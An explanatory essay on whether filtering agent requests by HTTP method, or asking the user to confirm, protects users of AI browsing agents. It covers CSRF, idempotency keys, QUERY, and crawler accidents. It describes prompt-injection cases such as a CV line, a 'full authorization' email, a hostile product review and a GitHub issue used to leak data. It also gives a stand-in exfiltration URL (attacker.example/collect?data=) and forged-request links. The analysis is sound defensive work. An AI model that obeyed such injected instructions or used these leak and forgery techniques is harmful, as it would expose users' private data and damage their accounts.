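# Safe and side-effecting web requests as a safeguard for AI browsing agents

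## HTTP requests and how browsing agents use them

HTTP, the Hypertext Transfer Protocol, is the set of rules by which browsers and other programs request pages from websites and send data to them. Every HTTP request carries a method, a word such as GET or POST that names the kind of request. Some methods count as safe, meaning that the program sending the request asks only for information. Requests with other methods may change something on the server, for instance by placing an order, posting a message or deleting a file. The distinction exists so that search engines can crawl the web and browsers can load pages ahead of time without accidentally causing such changes.

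A browsing agent is a language model that reads web pages and acts on them by fetching addresses, clicking, typing and submitting forms. Some AI companies use the distinction between safe and side-effecting requests to limit what their agents can do, allowing only requests that use safe HTTP methods. Many companies have the agent ask the user before making a purchase, sending a message or deleting something. Whether either safeguard works depends largely on what happens between the click and the website's server.

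### The parts of a request

A request always has a method and an address. It may also have headers, which are labelled lines of extra information (the type of program that is asking, say), and a body, which is a block of data for the server to process. Fielding, Nottingham and Reschke, in *HTTP Semantics*, the protocol's current specification, call the body "content", but the older word is still common. A made-up request that puts one item into a shopping cart could look like this:

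```
POST /cart HTTP/1.1
Host: shop.example
Cookie: session=7f3k9
Content-Type: application/x-www-form-urlencoded

item=4417&quantity=1
```

The first line gives the method and the path within the site, and the Host line gives the rest of the address. The body comes after the blank line. The server replies with a numeric status code (200 for success, 404 for a page it cannot find) and usually some content, such as the next page.

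Addresses can also carry data. In shop.example/search?q=kettle, everything after the question mark is data for the shop. Many search boxes work this way, sending a GET request with the user's words in the address. Fielding and colleagues warn that this can expose sensitive information, and they suggest POST as an alternative because it puts the words in the body of the request. So a POST request may be only a search, and a GET request always sends the server some information, even if only the address.

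HTTP is also stateless, meaning that each request has to make sense on its own. An online shop therefore needs a way to tell that a request to place an order comes from the person who signed in five minutes earlier. It usually does this with a cookie, a small piece of data that the server gives the browser to keep. MDN's *Using HTTP cookies*, part of Mozilla's documentation for web developers, describes a basic sign-in in four steps. The user submits a name and password. The server checks them and returns a cookie that contains a session ID. The browser attaches that cookie to its later requests to the same site. The server looks up the ID and, if it is still valid, responds with that user's version of the page. This is called a logged-in session, and it often includes the contents of a shopping cart.

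The browser attaches the cookie automatically, no matter who or what caused the request. If an agent clicks "Place order" in a browser where the user has signed in, the shop receives the user's session ID, just as it would if the user had clicked. According to MDN, the browser also sends the cookie by default when someone follows a link from another site, so an agent that follows a link from a stranger's page to the shop arrives signed in.

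### Safe and idempotent methods

GET requests a page or other resource. HEAD requests the same response without the content, which is useful for checking that a page exists. POST sends data, such as a completed form, a forum message or an order, which the server processes in a way that depends on the address. PUT replaces a resource with the version in the request body, PATCH changes part of one, and DELETE removes one. Ordinary links send GET, and ordinary web forms send GET or POST. The other methods come mostly from page scripts and from programs that are not browsers.

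An HTTP method is safe if the client, the program sending the request, asks for no change on the server. The server may still make small changes, such as writing a line in its log or adding one to a visitor count. It may also make much larger ones if the site's developers don't follow the rule that safe methods should only retrieve information. According to MDN's *Safe (HTTP Methods)*, standard server software such as Apache or Nginx cannot enforce this rule, so developers have to follow it in the site's own code. A side effect is any lasting change, wanted or not, and a state-changing request is one that causes a side effect, whatever its method. A GET request that deletes a file is therefore state-changing, even though GET is a safe method.

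A method has the other property, idempotence, if several identical requests are meant to have the same effect as one. For example, if a client sends the same DELETE request twice, the first response is 200 and the second is 404, but the document is gone after both (http.dev's *HTTP Methods*). Idempotence matters when a connection drops before the response arrives. The client can repeat a PUT with no additional effect, whereas repeating a POST might place a duplicate order. An idempotent request can still do harm, such as deleting the wrong file.

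| Method | What the client asks for | Safe | Idempotent |
|---|---|---|---|
| GET | the resource at this address | yes | yes |
| HEAD | the same, without the content | yes | yes |
| OPTIONS | which methods and features are available | yes | yes |
| PUT | replace the resource with the body | no | yes |
| DELETE | remove the resource | no | yes |
| POST | process the body | no | no |
| PATCH | change part of the resource | no | no |

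IANA's official list, the *Hypertext Transfer Protocol (HTTP) Method Registry* (2014), has dozens of other methods, most of them for specialised uses such as shared file storage and calendars. TRACE, a diagnostic method, is also safe, and so is QUERY, a recent addition for searches that need a request body.

A method filter sits outside the model and allows only requests that use a listed method, usually the safe methods GET, HEAD and OPTIONS. How much it blocks in practice depends on the tools the agent uses to reach the web.

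### Fetch tools and full browsers

Some agents have only a fetch tool, which retrieves the page at a given address and returns its text. Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, part of the developer documentation for its Claude models, describes a typical one. The model supplies only an address, so it cannot choose a method or write a body. The developer can list either the sites the tool may visit or the sites it may not, and can cap the number of fetches. The tool will not fetch an address unless it has already appeared in the conversation, for example in the user's message or an earlier search result. It does not support pages that scripts assemble inside the browser, which excludes many modern web pages.

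Other agents operate a full browser. OpenAI's *Operator System Card* (2025) describes an early one, which looked at screenshots and used a cursor and keyboard much as a person would. *CELLMATE* (Meng, Feng and colleagues, 2025), a proposal for restricting such agents, describes the usual loop, in which software captures the state of the current tab, the model picks an action such as click, scroll or navigate, and the browser carries it out. This repeats until the task is complete. These actions have no fixed meaning, so the same click command may open an email or delete it, depending on what is under the cursor. Meng and colleagues therefore place their controls on the HTTP traffic, because an action that affects the user's data must eventually produce a request to the website.

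One click can produce many requests. When the agent opens a product page, the browser first requests the page and then the images, style sheets and scripts it needs, often from other servers. For Amazon alone, Meng and colleagues had to permit four further groups of addresses, including the company's image servers and its advertising system. The scripts can then send their own requests, using any method their developers chose. Google's crawlers visit pages to read them, but according to http.dev they also send PUT, PATCH and DELETE requests, because scripts issue them while the crawler renders the page. HEAD, OPTIONS, PUT, PATCH and DELETE together make up less than 1.5% of Google's crawler requests, but a filter that checks request methods in a full browser will still encounter unsafe requests on pages the agent is only reading, and blocking them can stop a page from working.

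### One shopping task by both routes

Suppose a user wants an electric kettle for under $40 and asks an agent to find one and buy it.

An agent with a fetch tool begins with a search. The address of the shop's results page probably includes the search words, and a GET request would retrieve the page. But Anthropic's tool would not let the model compose that address, so the model would have to start from a general web search or a link that the user pasted in. Opening a product is another GET request. The model can read the name and price as long as the shop's server includes them in the page, instead of a script adding them later.

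A fetch normally can't add the kettle to the cart, because that step is a POST with the item number in the body. If the shop's developers had built "Add to cart" as a plain link, a fetch might trigger it, but the request would come from Anthropic's servers without the user's cookie, so the kettle would go into a cart that isn't the user's. A fetch can't place the order for the same reasons, so the user gets a recommendation and a link.

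With a full browser, the agent types "electric kettle" into the search box and presses Enter, which most likely sends a GET. Clicking a product sends another GET, along with requests for everything the page loads. When the agent clicks "Add to cart", the browser sends a POST with the user's session cookie. Viewing the cart sends a GET. Clicking "Place order" sends a POST, and the shop charges the card on file. Meng and colleagues found this pattern when they mapped part of Amazon's traffic, with GET used for viewing the cart and POST for updating it and placing the order.

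In this example, the HTTP method separates looking from buying fairly well, but it does not separate the order, which costs money, from the cart update, which the user can easily undo. A filter strict enough to stop the order also stops the cart update, which makes the agent much less useful for shopping. A finer rule has to consider the address as well as the method. A confirmation prompt, which asks the user to approve a step before the agent takes it, can come later in the task. OpenAI's policy for Operator called for one just before the agent completed a purchase, after it had finished the search and filled the cart.

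### Prompt injection and three kinds of harm

Agents read pages written by strangers, which exposes them to prompt injection, where text in the content an agent reads is written so that the model follows it as an instruction. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written by David C for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a job applicant who hides a line in a CV telling the screening model to approve it for interview. The trick can work because a language model receives the employer's instructions and the CV as one stretch of text and predicts what comes next, with no built-in boundary between instructions and the material to be assessed. David C therefore doubts that the problem will ever be completely fixed. The attacks have also become less crude. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) reproduces an email that reads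 like routine office correspondence but includes a passing claim that the reader's assistant has "full authorization" to look up employee details and submit them to an outside address. In testing with one particular user request, the attack worked half the time.

An agent can take unwanted actions without an attacker. In a document on a later version of Operator, OpenAI (2025) distinguishes between the model acting against the user's intent by mistake and something on the screen inducing it to do so. Before adding safeguards to the original Operator, OpenAI ran it on 100 tasks of the sort it expected from users and counted 13 errors that caused some nuisance. Users could have reversed eight of them within minutes. The rest included an email to the wrong recipient and a medication reminder with the wrong date. That model is several generations old, so its error rate is a poor guide to current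 models, but the kind of error is familiar. In the shopping example, it would be buying the wrong kettle.

An attacker can produce the same result on purpose. Meng and colleagues assume an attacker who can post a product review on Amazon but does not control the site. The review might tell the agent to order a different item, or to go to another site where the user is signed in and delete something. The resulting request goes to the real site with the user's real cookie, and nothing in its method or headers distinguishes it from a request the user wanted.

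Private data can also leak through a request that changes nothing. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes how injected text can lead the model to load an address such as attacker.example/collect?data=, with private data added after the equals sign. The attacker then reads the data in the server's log. The request is an ordinary GET, and the server only records it, which the definition of a safe method allows. The user may not notice, because the request can happen in the background, for instance when an image loads. Meng and colleagues describe an attack on Operator with the same aim. A user asked the agent to look into an issue on GitHub, a site where programmers share code, and the issue contained instructions to collect the user's private email address from another site, Hacker News, and pass it to the attacker.

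How well a method filter works against these harms depends largely on whether websites keep side effects out of GET, and on how much useful work an agent can do without POST. The filter would not stop an agent from leaking data in a URL, because that leak uses a GET request, which the filter allows. A confirmation prompt could in principle catch all three harms, provided that it appears at the right step and the user reads it before clicking yes.

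## What the HTTP specification promises and what it leaves to websites

A method filter allows or blocks a request before it is sent, so it has to infer the request's effect from its method. The only basis for that inference is a rule in the HTTP specification. The rule is enough to determine who is at fault when a GET deletes something and what mistakes a filter is bound to make, but how often websites break the rule has to be measured.

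### The rule from 1994 to today

The idea that GET requests should have no side effects is older than the first HTTP specification. In the mailing-list post *An alarming trend in METHOD=POST forms (an FYI)*, Berners-Lee (1994) described GET as a request that changes nothing anywhere and commits the user to nothing beyond the cost of access. Kaphan (1995), writing from Amazon, gave a practical reason. A cache answers requests with saved copies of pages, so the original server may never receive those requests. If a GET were supposed to change something on the server, a cache could prevent the change without anyone noticing. Kaphan called the absence of side effects a convention and thought it pointless to try to stop developers who wanted to break it.

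The Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF) publishes the internet's protocols in numbered documents called RFCs. The security considerations in the first one for HTTP, RFC 1945 (1996), included the rule that GET and HEAD "should never" do anything except retrieve information. They also allowed browsers to present other methods, such as POST, in a special way. The passage, which Connected's *Safe Methods* reproduces, begins by reminding programmers that their software represents the user and should make the user aware of actions with unexpected consequences. RFC 2068 (1997) moved the rule into the main description of methods and added PUT and DELETE to the examples of unsafe ones, as the later page of Connected's *Safe Methods* shows.

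Fielding's *Hypertext Transfer Protocol*, or RFC 2616 (1999), changed "should never" to "SHOULD NOT". The IETF gives such capitalized terms fixed meanings. MUST allows no exceptions, whereas SHOULD NOT allows them if the developer has understood and weighed the consequences. During a dispute over Google Web Accelerator, a program that loaded links in advance, the web developer Willison (2005) used this allowance to argue in *Fighting RFCs with RFCs* that putting delete links behind a login was an acceptable exception. He later withdrew the argument after readers pointed out that a malicious page could trigger those links in a signed-in user's browser.

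The current specification is RFC 9110, *HTTP Semantics* (Fielding et al., 2022). *HTTP Semantics* defines a method as safe if its defined meaning is "essentially read-only". On many sites, part of the address selects an action, as in page?do=delete. If that action is unsafe, the site's owner MUST disable it for requests that use a safe method. This requirement is stricter than the 1999 wording, but nothing in the protocol enforces it.

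### Who is responsible for a side effect

The word "safe" describes what the client asks for, and the server may still make changes of its own. Fielding and colleagues add that reasonable use of a safe method should not cause harm, loss of property or an unusual burden on the server. They accept that it sometimes has unwanted side effects. For example, log entries may fill the disk until the server fails, and a click on an advertisement often costs the advertiser money. But they state that the client cannot be held accountable for changes it did not request.

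The definition of "safe" is mainly about accountability. In a 2002 discussion, Graham Klyne suggested that "safe" might mean having no visible side effects, and Prescod (2002) replied that the specification is about responsibility. The World Wide Web Consortium (W3C), which develops many of the web's standards, later took the same view. Jacobs (2004), in *URIs, Addressability, and the use of HTTP GET and POST*, illustrates it with a mailing list that emails new subscribers a confirmation link. He says the link should open a page with a "Confirm" button that sends a POST. If opening the link is enough to confirm the subscription, a mail program that loads links ahead of time will sign the user up without their knowledge, and Jacobs puts the fault with the server. He likewise rejects notices telling visitors that they accept a site's terms by following a link, because anyone can link to the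 same page without showing the terms.

Under the specification, a user whose agent opens the wrong link is not to blame for the damage, but the specification doesn't undo it. The user may be stuck with an unwanted subscription, which is a small nuisance, or a deleted account, which could be a serious loss.

The reasoning also fits crawlers better than browsing agents. A crawler follows a link labelled "Delete" without understanding the label, so we can reasonably say that it didn't ask for a deletion. But a language model can read the label. If it follows the link because the user told it to delete a file, the user wanted the deletion, even though the request was a GET. If an injected instruction led it there, the attacker wanted the deletion. Fielding and colleagues define safety by the meaning of the method, so all of these requests are equally safe under their definition.

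### What software and site owners should do

In the specification, Fielding and colleagues write that a browser or other program acting for a user SHOULD distinguish safe from unsafe methods when it presents possible actions, so that the user knows about an unsafe action before it happens. The W3C's *Style Guide* expressed the hope that browsers would show a special cursor when the user was about to make a commitment. Berners-Lee (1998), in *User Agent Watch Points*, complained that browser designs had often failed to convey the protocol's meaning to users.

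Web design has since made it harder to tell by looking whether a click will send a GET or a POST request. Brocklehurst (2015), in *HTTP Safety Doesn't Happen by Accident*, recalls that links used to send GET and form buttons usually sent POST, so people could roughly tell which was which. Style sheets can now make a button look like a link, and scripts can send either kind of request without a click. An agent that works from screenshots has the same difficulty as a person, but the software around it can inspect each outgoing request.

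Fielding and colleagues also explain that the distinction lets a program limit the automated use of unsafe methods while it handles content that may be untrustworthy, which comes close to describing a method filter. A browsing agent on a stranger's web page fits that description well. The IETF's text therefore supports filtering by method, and its advice about presenting unsafe actions to the user supports confirmation prompts, but neither passage offers evidence that these safeguards work.

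A secure programming guide from The Linux Documentation Project suggests how sites can comply without breaking old links. If a request for an action arrives by any method except POST, the site should show a filled-in form and ask the user to confirm. The user has to click once more, but a program that only opens the link changes nothing. An agent with a method filter would stop at the form, because submitting it requires a POST request.

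### Can a client know in advance?

A filter has to determine whether a request is safe before it goes out, and the designers of HTTP disagreed about whether that was possible, or even necessary. In 1996 a developer named Mike Meyer told the HTTP working group that he routinely built applications whose GET requests were not harmless to repeat, because he was writing for a captive audience. Fielding (1996) answered that Meyer was accepting personal responsibility for any resulting loss of property. He wrote that the rule against such requests protects users whatever the developer intends, and that the client has to determine whether a method is safe before using it for the first time, so a notice in the server's response would come too late.

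Holtman (1998), in *The Safe Response Header Field*, proposed such a notice anyway, for a narrower purpose. When a user reloaded a page that had come from a POST, HTTP required the browser to ask for confirmation before sending the POST again. Holtman thought the usual dialog box, "repost form data?", confused many people. Under his proposal, RFC 2310, a server could add "Safe: yes" to its response, and the browser could then repeat the request without asking. The header arrived after the first request had been sent, so it could not warn the browser about that request. It could not warn of an unsafe GET either, because Holtman considered GET safe by definition and told clients to ignore "Safe: no" on GET responses. The IETF now lists the proposal as historic.

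Dan Connolly wanted a firm principle that safe methods must not be used to buy, agree or modify. Larry Masinter, who had taken part in the working group's discussions, objected that whether a request is safe, even a GET, ultimately depends on what the server does with it and not on the method (Masinter, 2002). He added that in most of the cases the group had examined, clients needed to know whether a request was safe only after the fact. He also saw no use for software that submitted forms in advance.

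Masinter is right on the facts, and the current specification supports him by allowing for servers that misbehave. But his remark about use cases does not apply to browsing agents, which submit forms, often with nobody watching. An agent about to click "Place order" needs to know beforehand what the click will do, and the server's response arrives only after the order. In a later discussion of the same wording, Rose inferred that the client has to judge safety alone because it cannot know what the server is really doing.

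A filter therefore has to rely on the method, as Fielding recommended, even though the method may be wrong, as Masinter pointed out. Sites could also describe their operations in advance. Jacobs mentions a plan for a "safe" label in the machine-readable descriptions that some web services publish. A client could read such a label before sending a request, but it would still have to trust the site to label its operations correctly.

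### A filter's two kinds of error

Comparing the method with the actual effect gives four cases, and a filter gets two of them wrong.

| | Changes nothing that matters to the user | Changes something |
|---|---|---|
| GET (filter passes it) | Correct: opening a product page | Error: opening a link that confirms a subscription |
| POST (filter blocks it) | Error: searching a catalogue | Correct: placing an order |

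Some websites are known to change data in response to GET requests. RFC 2616 acknowledged that some dynamic pages have side effects by design. In an IETF draft on repeated requests, Nottingham reports that many GET requests have been widely observed to have side effects, though he gives no rate. A developer may use GET for such an action simply because a link is easier to put in an email than a form is.

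Websites often have good engineering reasons to use POST for requests that only read data. Holtman notes that a form may be very long, include a file to upload, or hold information that should not appear in an address. In other cases, using POST is poor design. Jacobs describes a manufacturer that built its catalogue search with POST, so a customer who looks up a telephone by catalogue number can't bookmark the result or send it to colleagues.

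Some systems send nearly everything by POST. GraphQL is a language in which a page's scripts ask a server for exactly the data they need, usually by sending the request to a single address. These two invented requests have the same method and address, but the first looks up an order and the second cancels it:

```
POST /graphql
{"query": "query { order(id: 842) { status } }"}

POST /graphql
{"query": "mutation { cancelOrder(id: 842) { status } }"}
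```

GraphQL labels reads "query" and writes "mutation", so a filter that read the body could use these labels, although a careless developer can still put a side effect behind a query. JSON-RPC, a format for calling functions on a server, has no such labels. The body contains a function name chosen by the site's developers, such as getInvoice or closeAccount, so a filter would need a list of what each function does. A filter that checks only the HTTP method blocks all of these requests.

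A hypothetical example can show how the two errors add up. Suppose an agent with a full browser sends 900 GET requests and 100 POST requests, and that 9 of the GETs change something that matters to the user, while 60 of the POSTs only read data. Updates to visitor counters and new log entries don't count as changes here.

| Invented log | Only reads | Changes something | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
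| GET, passed | 891 | 9 | 900 |
| POST, blocked | 60 | 40 | 100 |
| Total | 951 | 49 | 1,000 |

The filter wrongly passes nine requests and wrongly blocks 60. Those nine are only 1% of the requests it passes, but 18% of the 49 that change something. If 2% of GETs changed something, the filter would miss 18 of 58 state-changing requests, or 31%. GETs are so much more common than POSTs that even rare violations make up a large share of state-changing requests. Of the requests the filter blocks, 60% are harmless.

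These percentages depend entirely on the invented inputs, and all changes count equally in them, though one of the nine might mark a message as read and another might delete the whole mailbox. They also apply only to an agent doing ordinary work. An attacker who can steer the agent can look for one harmful GET on a site where the user is likely to be signed in, and in that case the average rate matters less than whether such a link exists.

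### Cross-site request forgery

Web developers have dealt with a version of this attack, called cross-site request forgery, for decades. Suppose a user is signed in to shop.example and then visits attacker.example. The attacker's page contains an image whose address is shop.example/account?do=close. When the browser tries to load the image, it sends a GET request to the shop. In the original form of the attack, the browser also attaches the user's session cookie, so the request appears to come from the customer and the shop closes the account. The attack works even though the attacker never reads the shop's response.

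Jacobs gives an early example with a company network instead of a shop. A page outside the company's firewall links to a system inside it, and an employee who follows the link unwittingly activates a function there. This weakness changed Willison's mind about delete links behind a login, since the attacker's page exploits the session that the login provides. He then learned that switching to POST was no defence by itself, because the attacker's page can contain a hidden form addressed to the shop and a script that submits it as soon as the page opens.

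Sites now have two common protections, and both depend on the distinction between safe and unsafe methods. One is a cookie setting called SameSite. When it is set to Lax, the browser attaches the cookie to a request from another site only if the request uses a safe method and opens a new page in the tab, as an ordinary link does. This stops the hidden form, which sends a POST, and the image, which doesn't open a new page. An attacker can still use a plain link to shop.example/account?do=close, or a script on their own page that sends the browser to that address. Setting SameSite to Strict would withhold the cookie in those cases too, but a customer who followed a link to the shop from a search engine or an email would appear signed out.

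The other protection is a token, a secret random value that the shop puts in each of its own forms. The attacker's page can't read the value, so a forged form arrives without it and the shop rejects it. Frameworks, the ready-made software developers use to build sites, often include this check but typically skip it for safe methods. Django, for example, does not require a token on GET, HEAD, OPTIONS or TRACE requests. This is reasonable if those requests change nothing, but if a developer has put an action behind a GET, the framework doesn't check for a token before the action runs.

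Neither protection does much against prompt injection that ends in a POST. An agent that clicks "Place order" on the shop's real page sends the shop's own token, and the browser includes the cookie because the request comes from the shop's own site. A method filter would block that request even though the site's protections allow it.

All three protections assume that a GET request doesn't change anything, so they fail together when a website lets one do so. Suppose the agent follows an injected instruction to open shop.example/account?do=close. The filter passes the request because it is a GET, and the framework skips the token check for the same reason. The browser attaches a Lax cookie because the agent is opening a page with a safe method. If the agent enters the address directly, the browser would normally attach even a Strict cookie, as it does when a person types an address. A fetch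 tool would avoid this attack because it doesn't send the user's cookies.

### Retrying an order after a time-out

An agent can also do damage by sending a legitimate request twice. Suppose a user asks for one kettle, the agent clicks "Place order", and the connection drops before a reply arrives. The request may never have reached the shop, or the shop may have accepted the order and only the reply was lost. The agent sees the same error page in both cases. If it clicks again, the user may get two kettles. In *Resubmitting POSTS*, Cox (1994) worried about the same outcome when browsers reloaded a page by resending its POST.

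The HTTP specification by Fielding and colleagues lets a client repeat idempotent requests automatically. A client SHOULD NOT automatically repeat a request that uses another method, such as the POST that places an order, unless it knows that the request is idempotent or can detect that the first one never took effect. A proxy, which passes requests between client and server, MUST NOT automatically retry non-idempotent requests. Software can break these rules too. Nottingham notes that some clients and intermediaries retry on their own, inconsistently, and that no website can count on receiving a request only once.

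The usual remedy is an idempotency key. The client generates a random identifier for the purchase and sends it with the order, often in a header:

```
POST /orders HTTP/1.1
Host: shop.example
Idempotency-Key: 9b2e61c4

item=4417&quantity=1
```

The server first looks up the key. If the key is new, the server records it, places the order and saves the result. When the client sends the same request again after the time-out, the server finds the key and returns the saved result instead of placing a second order. The server has to record the key before starting the order, because otherwise two copies arriving at nearly the same moment could both go through. *Method Semantics*, an online lesson about HTTP, shows why this is needed with a checkout example in which the user taps again, the app retries by itself, and the card may have been charged once, twice or not at all.

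The key gives an agent limited protection because it identifies only one attempt at a purchase, and the model can start another. If the browser resends the request, the key stays the same. If the model reads the error page, returns to the kettle, adds it to the cart and checks out again, the shop's page will probably generate a new key, and the server will receive a second valid order. A careful agent would check the order history before trying again, which takes only a GET request. Fielding and colleagues describe a similar approach for version-control programs, which can check the server's current state after a failed connection and then repeat only what is missing.

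Repeating a series of steps can also cause errors even when each step is harmless to repeat, because, as RFC 2616 notes, a sequence of idempotent requests is not necessarily idempotent. Suppose the user asks the agent to add one more kettle to a cart that already holds one. The agent reads the quantity as 1 and sends a PUT that sets it to 2, but the reply gets lost. Repeating the PUT would do no harm, but an agent that starts the task over reads the quantity as 2 and sets it to 3.

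### QUERY, a safe method with a body

The IETF has now defined a method for read-only requests that would otherwise use POST. *The HTTP QUERY Method* (Reschke, Snell and Bishop, 2026) specifies QUERY, which carries its search terms in the body, as POST does, but counts as both safe and idempotent. It appeared in June 2026 as RFC 10008, a Proposed Standard. Jacobs records that an IETF meeting had already discussed a "safe POST" in December 1996 without reaching agreement.

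Reschke and colleagues give the example of searching a news feed. A program can use GET and put the search terms in the address, but a long search may exceed the length limit of some system along the way. It can also put the terms in the body of a POST request, but then only someone who knows that particular site can tell that the request is just a search. QUERY also carries the terms in the body, but the method identifies the request as a read.

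QUERY could reduce the number of harmless requests that a method filter blocks. If sites in the invented log moved 45 of the 60 read-only POST requests to QUERY, and the filter allowed QUERY, it would wrongly block 15 requests instead of 60. The nine GET requests that change data would still pass. The gain depends on sites adopting QUERY, and developers who gave GET requests side effects could do the same with QUERY.

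Allowing QUERY also increases the amount of data an attacker could extract through the agent. A program can attach a body to a GET, but Fielding and colleagues advise against it except by arrangement with the server, so a filter could remove such bodies and break very little. It can't do the same with QUERY, which needs its body. A filter that allows QUERY therefore lets the agent send out large blocks of text, perhaps a whole document or email thread, in a request that officially only reads. GET already allows leaks through the address, but they are much smaller.

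In the security section of RFC 10008, Reschke and colleagues say that servers and intermediaries are more likely to log addresses than request bodies, and they give this as a reason to use QUERY for sensitive searches. This protects users whose search terms would otherwise be recorded in a stranger's log. But a company that checks its own logs of outgoing addresses for leaked data could miss what an agent sent in a body.

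Browsers will require a preflight for QUERY requests from one site's scripts to another site. In a preflight, the browser first sends an OPTIONS request to check whether the receiving server permits the real one. This protects servers from unwanted requests, but it would not stop a leak, because an attacker who runs the receiving server can grant permission. A fetch tool outside the browser also need not send a preflight. A filter could instead allow QUERY only to approved sites, or limit the size of the body, but then it would be checking more than the method.

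## Crawlers, prefetchers and link scanners that set off actions

Programs much simpler than a browsing agent, such as search crawlers, prefetchers and email scanners, have been opening links automatically since the 1990s. Their accidents are the longest record of what happens when software relies on GET requests being safe. These programs don't understand the pages they load, so when one of them deletes something, the cause is usually a website that let a GET request trigger the deletion.

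### Google Web Accelerator

On 4 May 2005, Google released a test version of Web Accelerator, which sped up browsing partly by prefetching, or loading pages before the user asked for them. It chose pages partly by tracking mouse movements and overall traffic to sites, according to Search Engine Watch's *New Google Software Attempts to Speed Up Your Web Browsing Experience*. Nottingham (2005) recalls in *Prefetching (again)* that caching researchers had studied prefetching heavily in the late 1990s and decided it wasn't worth the overhead for shared caches. But Web Accelerator ran on the user's own computer, alongside a browser signed in to the user's accounts.

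The next day, a few customers of the software company 37signals reported that pages were disappearing from Backpack, its new personal organiser. Jason (2005), in *Google Web Accelerator*, a post on the company's blog, explained that the program was in effect clicking every link on a page, including the ones that deleted things. The "Are you sure?" prompts on those links made no difference. An invented link of this kind shows why:

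```
<a href="/page/delete/17"
   onclick="return confirm('Are you sure?')">Delete</a>
```

When a person clicks the link, the browser runs the "onclick" script, shows the question, and requests the address only if the person agrees. Web Accelerator fetched the "href" address without running the script, so the question never appeared. The server received an ordinary GET request from a signed-in customer and deleted the page.

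Jason Fried, the president of 37signals, told Hicks (2005) in *Googles Accelerator Breaks Web Apps, Security* that the company blocked Web Accelerator within 30 minutes of working out the cause. Prefetch requests carried the header "X-Moz: prefetch", so a site could refuse any request that had it. Hicks reports deleted accounts on both Backpack and Basecamp, the company's project-management service, whereas the blog post mentions only Backpack pages. Neither gives a number more precise than "a few" users. Mike Rumble, a programmer, told Hicks that he kept getting signed out of his Apple email, and he blamed Web Accelerator for fetching the sign-out link as soon as he had signed in.

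The evidence of exactly what the program fetched is mixed. Among the 158 comments under Jason's post, one developer reported that it had deleted sales leads from a company database, but others couldn't reproduce the deletions on their own sites. One found that the program loaded a link only after the mouse had rested on it for about half a second. Another suspected a separate fault, in which Google's servers sometimes showed people pages saved for other users, so someone might have clicked "Delete" on a stranger's page. Google confirmed that fault on as many as five sites. But 37signals had traced its own losses to prefetching, and Marissa Mayer, then Google's director of consumer web products, conceded to Hicks that Google's assumptions about links might be wrong.

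Google had tried to avoid harmful links. Mayer said that the program skipped addresses containing a question mark, because links that performed actions such as deletion typically had one. It also skipped encrypted pages. Like the request method, the question mark is only a rough sign of what a link does. The address of a harmless search for kettles usually contains one, and a link that deletes a page could use an address without one, such as the invented /page/delete/17.

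### Who was at fault

Fried admitted that his company's deletions should technically have used buttons instead of links. His colleague David Heinemeier Hansson defended the links in the comments on Fried's post. Like Willison, he thought the specification's "SHOULD NOT" left room for such links behind a login page, which crawlers had never got past. He also thought Google had ignored how the web worked. In *Breaking the Web We Have*, Bicking put much of the blame on HTML, which had no simple way to make a link send a POST. Developers who wanted a small "delete" link next to each item used GET because the alternative was a full form or a script.

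Ryan Tomayko replied to Hansson that sites relying on unsafe GETs were like sites that worked only in Internet Explorer, because they limited what other software could safely do with them. Other commenters pointed out that links that trigger unsafe GETs were a security hole with or without Web Accelerator, and that argument changed Willison's mind. Google's own sites used unsafe GETs too. Its Blogger service deleted comments through a plain link, and a commenter showed that any web page could switch a visitor's Google language to Pig Latin by loading one address.

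The specification supports Tomayko, but Hansson was right about the practical problem. Users lost data because a client relied on a rule that many sites did not follow. Even Tomayko thought Google should add a special mode to recognise common misuse of GET.

When Google relaunched the program in October 2005, it still used a link's address to decide whether to prefetch it. According to a description that circulated among WordPress developers, it did not prefetch encrypted pages or links containing a question mark. Prodoehl (2005), one of those developers, argued in *Google Web Accelerator* that WordPress should follow the HTTP rule anyway. In *Google at it again*, Bicking (2005) at first called the new version worse, partly because Google had apparently dropped the header that let sites refuse prefetching. He then conceded in the comments that skipping links with question marks was some improvement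 and might be enough.

Bicking also raised a case that the rule handles badly. Opening an email should be a GET because the user is only reading, but the site also needs to mark the message as read. If a prefetcher loaded every message in an inbox, the user could no longer tell which ones were new. A browsing agent that opens messages to summarise them has the same effect.

### Search crawlers that deleted content

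A crawler normally has no login, so it can only set off actions that a site has left open to the public. A blog by a Google employee, ImperialViolet (2005), describes an early wiki with a "Delete this page" link on every page. Google's crawler followed the links and erased the site. The owner emailed Google to ask for his website back, and the employee believed Google had recovered it from the copies its crawler had saved.

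The best-documented case is much smaller. In January 2009, QuimaxW (2009) reported in *Mythweb...beware the googlebot* that Google's crawler, Googlebot, had deleted every television recording on his home server. A line he posted from the server's log shows a GET request for an address containing "recorded?delete=yes" and a channel number. Another forum member suspected an impostor, since anyone can write "Googlebot" in a request's headers, but a third looked up the IP address and found that it belonged to googlebot.com. The server had no password, and QuimaxW thought Google had found its address in his forum profile. The crawler also damaged his list of scheduled recordings, and he planned to start again with a blank database and a password. Googlebot did not apply Web Accelerator's question-mark rule, which would have spared these recordings.

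Some sites had a login check that worked only in a browser. The Daily WTF, a site that collects stories of software failures, describes a government website that lost all its content six days after launch. An employee had copied text from one page to another, including an "edit" link. The site kept strangers out by checking for a cookie and running a script that sent them to the login page. Googlebot kept no cookies and ran no scripts at the time, so it got past both checks and followed every link, including "Delete Page". The developer, Josh Breckman, restored an older version from a backup. He explained the flaw to his managers, who told the client never to copy and paste content between pages. Search Engine Roundtable also blamed the site in *GoogleBot Deletes All Of Webmasters Content; Site Owner's Fault*.

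Readers of The Daily WTF replied with similar stories, which are anonymous and hard to check. In one, a developer's boss wanted a search feature covering the company's whole site, so the developer let an indexing program, ht://Dig, crawl it as an administrator, and it followed all the delete links. This is the crawler story closest to a browsing agent in a signed-in browser, because someone had deliberately given the program an account with permission to delete.

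### Email scanners and one-click unsubscribe

Email security software opens links to check them for malware or fraud, often before the recipient has seen the message. If opening a link is enough to unsubscribe, the scanner unsubscribes the recipient. *Signaling One-Click Functionality for List Email Headers* (Levine and Herkula, 2017) describes this as a known problem with the List-Unsubscribe header, a line in a marketing email that contains an unsubscribe address. The sender can't tell whether a request came from a person or a scanner. Many senders therefore made the link open a page with a confirmation button, which a scanner would not press.

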